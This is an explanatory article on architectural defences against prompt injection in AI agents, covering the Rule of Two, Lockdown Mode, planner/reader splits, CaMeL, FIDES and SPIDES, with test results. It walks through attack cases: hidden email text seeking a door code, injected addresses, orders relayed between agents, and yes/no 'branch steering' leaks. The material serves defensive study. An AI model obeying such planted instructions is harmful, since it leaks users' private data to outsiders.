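Training and filters make a model less likely to obey a planted instruction, but a persistent attacker often gets past them. *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper, tested 12 published defences, most of which had reported attack success rates near zero. Attacks adapted to each defence succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, and the 500 participants in a competition collectively beat all 12 (Willison, 2025, *New prompt injection papers*).

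Some designs therefore assume that attackers will fool the model, and limit what it can do afterwards. OpenAI compares this to customer service, where a company expects customers to mislead its staff now and then, so its software caps the refunds an employee can give. These designs can keep private data from outsiders in many tasks, but they make the agent less useful, and the guarantee each one offers has gaps.

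### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the lethal trifecta into a limit for developers. Until models can reliably detect injections, an agent working on its own should have no more than two of these properties in a session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy input;
- B: it has access to private data or sensitive systems;
- C: it can change something or communicate with the outside.

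Property C is broader than the trifecta's "outside communication" because it includes changes such as deleting files. Willison likes the broader definition because it covers attacks that do damage without stealing anything.

Meta's main example is an email assistant. If it reads only messages from trusted senders, it receives no untrusted input and can reply freely. If it works in a test environment without real mail, it has no private data to leak. If it can write only to trusted recipients, or a person checks every draft, a spam email can't make it forward the inbox to an outsider.

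An agent can also give up one property to gain another during a session. For example, it could research a topic on the open web, then permanently lose outside communication before it opens the company's files. The software has to close every channel, including images in the final answer, because hostile text from the web may still be in the agent's context window. Going online after reading private files is unsafe because their contents are still in the context window.

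The rule works only if the agent really lacks the property it is supposed to lack. The travel assistant in Meta's example reads the web and knows the user's private details. To remove property C, the user confirms every booking, and the agent opens only web addresses that trusted sources returned, not ones it composed itself. An attacker who can get prepared addresses into those sources can still learn private data from which ones the agent opens. Meta warns that users may confirm an action without reading it.

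### Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting, removes most of the routes by which private data could reach an outsider. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on February 13 for organizations such as companies, schools and healthcare providers. On June 4, OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts, including free ones.

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
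|---|---|
| Web browsing | Only copies of pages that OpenAI has stored |
| Images from the web | Off |
| Deep Research and agent mode | Off |
| Programs made in Canvas, ChatGPT's editor | No network access |
| Downloading files for analysis | Off, but the user can still upload files |
| Memory and sharing of conversations | Unchanged |
| Codex's network access | Unchanged |

Reading only stored copies of web pages also stops an agent from leaking data through its choice of which addresses to open from a set an attacker prepared. ChatGPT's normal check does not stop this leak. With stored copies, however, search results may be old or missing.

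Connected apps remain the largest gap. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services and write actions where they conflict with its protections. In company-managed workspaces, administrators choose which apps and actions to allow, and OpenAI ranks app actions to help them decide. If they allow an app that can post publicly, an attacker could still use it to leak private data.

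Lockdown Mode also doesn't stop prompt injections from changing ChatGPT's answers. A planted instruction could make ChatGPT advise the user to turn the setting off, which takes only a few clicks for a single chat. OpenAI says the setting isn't guaranteed to prevent every leak and that most users don't need it.

The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* says the added protection is worth the lost features for anyone who handles sensitive data. That seems right for a lawyer who uploads contracts and wants summaries, because that work needs none of the disabled features. An analyst who compares internal sales figures with today's news would lose access to the live news. A developer also has to restrict Codex separately.

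### One model plans and another reads

A developer can divide an agent's work between two models instead of taking features away from the whole agent. Willison (2023) proposed this in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. A planner receives the user's request and can call tools, while a reader with no tools reads the emails and web pages, which the planner never sees. Ordinary software passes values between the two models and shows the planner only the values' names, such as `$VAR1`. Rahman and Kim tested such a split and found no leaks.

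Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad" because it is complicated to build and less pleasant to use. The reader's output can still deceive the user. For example, a summary could include a request to paste an encoded string into a website.

Google DeepMind researchers later found another weakness. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and the planner has the reader find Bob's address in some meeting notes. Hostile text in the notes can't change the plan, but it can make the reader return the attacker's address, and the software then sends the document there.

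### Labels that follow the data

To fix this, the software has to know where each value came from. Keeping such a record is called taint tracking.

Google DeepMind's system CaMeL uses a program to control where data can go. Its planner turns the user's request into code in a restricted version of Python before any model reads the data (Willison, 2025, *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*). A special interpreter runs the code, tracks which values each new value came from, and checks a rule before each tool call. For example, a rule might allow email to known addresses but require the user's approval for any others.

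*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that lets the planner decide one step at a time. Each value has a label showing whether it is trusted and who may read it. When the agent combines values, the result is labeled untrusted if any source was untrusted, and only people who may read all the sources may read it.

If a tool returns data with a stricter label than the planner's context, FIDES hides the data in a variable. The planner can inspect the variable, but everything it does afterwards has the stricter label.

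### One email, step by step

Suppose a supplier named Sam sends an email, and the user tells the agent: "Summarize this email and reply to its sender with the summary." Hidden text in the email asks for the door code, 4471, which is in the company's building notes. The values might have these labels:

| Value | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Yes | Anyone |
| Sam's address, from the email's header | Yes, if the mail server has verified it | The user and Sam |
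| The text of the email | No | The user and Sam |
| The summary | No | The user and Sam |
| The building notes | Yes | The user and colleagues |
| A reply based on the email and the notes | No | Only the user |

"Trusted" means here that the address is genuine, not that Sam is honest. CaMeL's planner would write a program like this:

`email = get_last_email()`

`summary = ask_reader("Summarize this email", email.text)`

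`send_email(to=email.sender, body=summary)`

FIDES would make the same three calls one at a time:

1. The mail tool returns the email. FIDES shows the planner Sam's address and hides the text in a variable.
2. The planner asks the reader for a summary. The reader may obey the hidden text, but it has no tools and has never seen the notes, so it can't reveal the code. FIDES stores the summary in another variable.
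3. The planner asks to send the summary to Sam. The software checks that no untrusted text influenced the choice of tool or recipient, and that Sam may read the summary. Both are true, so it sends the reply.

Sam might receive a strange summary, but would learn nothing that wasn't in the original email. CaMeL could be stricter here. The rule in Willison's example treats an address taken from an email as untrusted, so the user would have to approve the reply unless Sam is a known contact.

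If the user now asks the agent to answer Sam's question using the building notes, the reader this time receives both texts and could put 4471 into the reply. But the reply's label allows only the user to read it, so the software won't send it to Sam. Writing the code backwards or in Base64 doesn't help, because the check depends on the reply's sources, not its wording. For the same reason, the check also blocks a harmless answer about parking.

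If the email asks for a reply to a different address, that address fails the recipient check because it comes from untrusted text. This closes the gap in the meeting notes example.

### The cost in usefulness

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on the 97 user tasks in AgentDojo. The last column averages the results for the test's four environments:

| Agent | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack |
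|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 84% |
| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 0 | 42% |
| FIDES with checks | 0 | 50% |

Security measures stopped the agent from completing many tasks, though hiding untrusted values recovered some of them. FIDES also did better with a stronger model, completing 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

There are two reasons to be cautious about the zeros. The researchers labelled a data field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so the test didn't measure what happens when somebody forgets a label. AgentDojo's own scoring also counted three successful attacks against FIDES, which the researchers rejected after inspecting them, for example because the rules allowed the action or the attack had only changed some text.

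In about a fifth of the tasks, the planner had to read the data before choosing the next step. The share was 44% in banking, where a user might ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. FIDES is designed to block payments in such tasks, and it usually does.

Newer models lose less of their ability to complete tasks under CaMeL. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL on professional tasks that a coordinating agent divides among four specialists. Completion fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The researchers had to document the exact format of every tool's output because CaMeL's planner writes its program before it can see any of that output.

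Planning in advance is much harder when an agent operates a computer through its screen, because the plan has to allow for many possible screens. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapted CaMeL to such agents and kept at most 57% of the larger commercial models' normal performance on OSWorld, a test of everyday computer tasks.

### When one agent gives orders to another

Peters-Gill and colleagues also found that a team of agents can leak data even if every agent runs CaMeL. In their demonstration, a user asked the team to send a summary of all job applicants to Julie on Slack. The applicant database contained an instruction to email the data to an outsider.

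The coordinator and the agent that read the database both treated the instruction as data. But the coordinator then pasted the summary into its order to a third agent, which sends messages. That agent treated the whole order as its user's request, so its planner added an email to the outsider.

The researchers' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each order into a message and a set of variables. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output, so text from a database has to be passed as a variable, which the next planner can't read.

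Each of five models faced 949 attacks. On average, 12.9% succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so these attacks were probably too weak to be a useful test of the best models. The demonstration is better evidence because it shows how untrusted text becomes a trusted order. Multi-CaMeL reduced the share of professional tasks completed by another 3.2 percentage points on average.

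### Web pages with labels

Labelling data is difficult in a browser because one page can contain a shop's prices, a stranger's review and the user's saved card. Extending the same-origin policy to agents doesn't separate these, since they all belong to the same site. An agent could still copy private account details into a public comment on that site.

In *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026), the site's operator labels the parts of each page. The agent sees `[var_2]` in place of the review. If it opens that variable, it needs the user's approval to click anything on a site where the user might have an account.

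The researchers tested SPIDES on 28 invented websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. Once a model had read untrusted text, they let the attacker choose its output, so the results don't depend on how well the model resists attacks or how cleverly they are worded. No attack succeeded against SPIDES, while 53 to 73% succeeded against SOPGuard, a defence based on the same-origin policy.

SPIDES completed 67 to 86% of the ordinary tasks, depending on the model. It asked for an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. The researchers assumed that users always distinguish safe requests from unsafe ones, but real users often fail to.

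### What each design guarantees

| Design | What it should prevent | What has to be true |
|---|---|---|
| Rule of Two | Theft through a planted instruction | The developer has really removed one of the three properties |
| Lockdown Mode | Requests from ChatGPT to an attacker's server | The setting stays on, and the permitted apps offer no way out |
| Planner and reader | Hostile text choosing the agent's tools | The reader's text never reaches the planner |
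| CaMeL | Hostile text adding steps to the plan, and data going where the rules forbid | The user's request contains no hostile text, and the rules are right |
| FIDES | Hostile text triggering important actions, and private data going directly to people who may not read it | The labels and rules are right |
| SPIDES | The same, in a browser | The user trusts the right sites, and their operators label the pages correctly |

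Most of these guarantees cover hostile instructions but not the model's own mistakes. For some actions, SPIDES lets private data go to any site if no untrusted text influenced the decision, on the assumption that the user wanted this. FIDES can use the same rule. An agent that misunderstands its task and publishes a private report on a public site could therefore pass the check. A developer can prevent this by also checking every time whether the recipient may read the data, but then the agent has to ask the user before it sends anything to a new recipient.

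### When every label becomes "secret"

Labels only get stricter as an agent combines values. An assistant that has read a salary file, a contract and a stranger's email in one session may end up with a context labeled as untrusted and readable only by its user. It then needs approval for nearly everything. Security researchers call this label creep.

*The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) simulated how much a better arrangement of agents can help. The simulation used no language models, and each task consisted of 20 tool calls, some of which returned sensitive data. Passing messages through a coordinator made label creep worse than connecting agents directly, because every message the coordinator passed on also affected its own label. With five agents and four sensitive calls, the coordinator raised the share of calls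 made under a "sensitive" label by about five percentage points.

Adding agents reduced label creep, since each one saw less data. Giving all the sensitive tools to a few agents also helped. But if every agent can talk to every other, going from five agents to 20 raises the number of connections to monitor from 10 to 190.

No arrangement solved the problem. Some label creep was certain because the simulation had no way to relax a label. The simulation measures how much the arrangement matters, but not how soon a real agent would become useless.

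A practical system needs controlled exceptions, as *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also argues. FIDES can limit the reader's answer to yes or no, or to a choice from a short list. A rule may then let the planner act on that answer, because a single "yes" can't contain a hidden instruction.

FlowSeal, the system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), uses a checker to compare outgoing text with all the sensitive records that may have influenced it. The checker can look for paraphrases and coded references, which an ordinary scanner would miss. But recognizing a paraphrase takes judgement, so the checker can fail in the same way as other detectors.

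### Who writes the rules?

The CaMeL paper acknowledges that someone has to write and update the rules. Willison worries about leaving this to users. He has worked on application security for two decades and still finds such rules difficult.

Software can get many labels from information that already exists. Costa and colleagues suggest taking an email's permitted readers from its sender and recipients. FlowSeal can use a system's existing access permissions. Those permissions may be too broad, but they still help against outsiders. If all staff can open a salary file, the agent could send it to the wrong colleague but not to an outsider.

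SPIDES depends on other companies to label their pages. Its designers compare these labels to the accessibility information that sites already provide. On a trusted site, SPIDES treats any part of a page without a label as trusted and public. If a shop adds a section for customer reviews and forgets to label it, SPIDES treats instructions in a stranger's review as the shop's own text. Treating unlabelled parts as untrusted would be safer, but the agent would then ask for many more approvals until sites finished labelling their pages.

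### What a yes or no can reveal

Labels don't stop an agent from revealing a secret through its choice of action. Suppose the user says, "If any of today's emails asks for a meeting, tell Sam I'm free on Friday." The reader gets all the emails, including one with the door code. Sam's email contains a hidden instruction to answer "yes" only if the code is below 5000. Sam can then tell whether it is below 5000 by whether he gets a message.

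If the rules allow yes-or-no answers, the message to Sam passes every check, because the user chose both its wording and its recipient. But Sam can learn which half of the possible codes contains the right one by seeing whether the message arrives. Fourteen such requests would be enough to find a four-digit code.

Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering, because hostile text picks a branch that was already in the plan. CaMeL and multi-CaMeL allow it. If an agent reads the screen, altered pixels can also pick the branch. Costa and colleagues also exclude leaks through the choice or timing of actions from FIDES's guarantee. To prevent leaks through the agent's choices completely, they would have to stop an agent that has read private data from taking almost any action an outsider can see.

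*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) adds that Python makes information flows hard to verify in advance, partly because an error can make a program jump to a different step. If a secret determines whether the error occurs, the program's next action can reveal something about the secret.

These leaks are slow, and a developer can often prevent them. In the example, the reader could answer the question for each email separately. Sam's email and the door code would then never be in the same context window, so Sam's hidden text couldn't make the answer depend on the code. This doesn't work when the question requires the reader to compare several documents.

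### Tasks that need all three parts

A support agent reads messages from strangers, looks up private records and sends replies. Under the Rule of Two, a person would have to supervise it. Labels can be more precise: if the label on a customer's record lists that customer as a permitted reader, the agent can send them their own order history but not somebody else's. The agent still has all three parts of the trifecta, but the software controls who can receive which data.

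Labels help less when somebody has to decide what to disclose. Suppose a journalist asks about a confidential contract that is labelled as readable only by staff. The company may want to confirm one fact and withhold the rest, and no existing label covers that decision. Meta recommends human approval for such cases. It is also researching the use of other AI agents as supervisors, which would again make security depend on a model's judgement.

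Hossain and colleagues' study showed that human approval is unreliable too, but taint tracking could make approval easier by picking out the values that people need to check. If an agent takes a bank account number from an emailed invoice, taint tracking marks the number as coming from untrusted text. The software can then show it next to the number in the company's supplier records, so that the user only has to review the difference.
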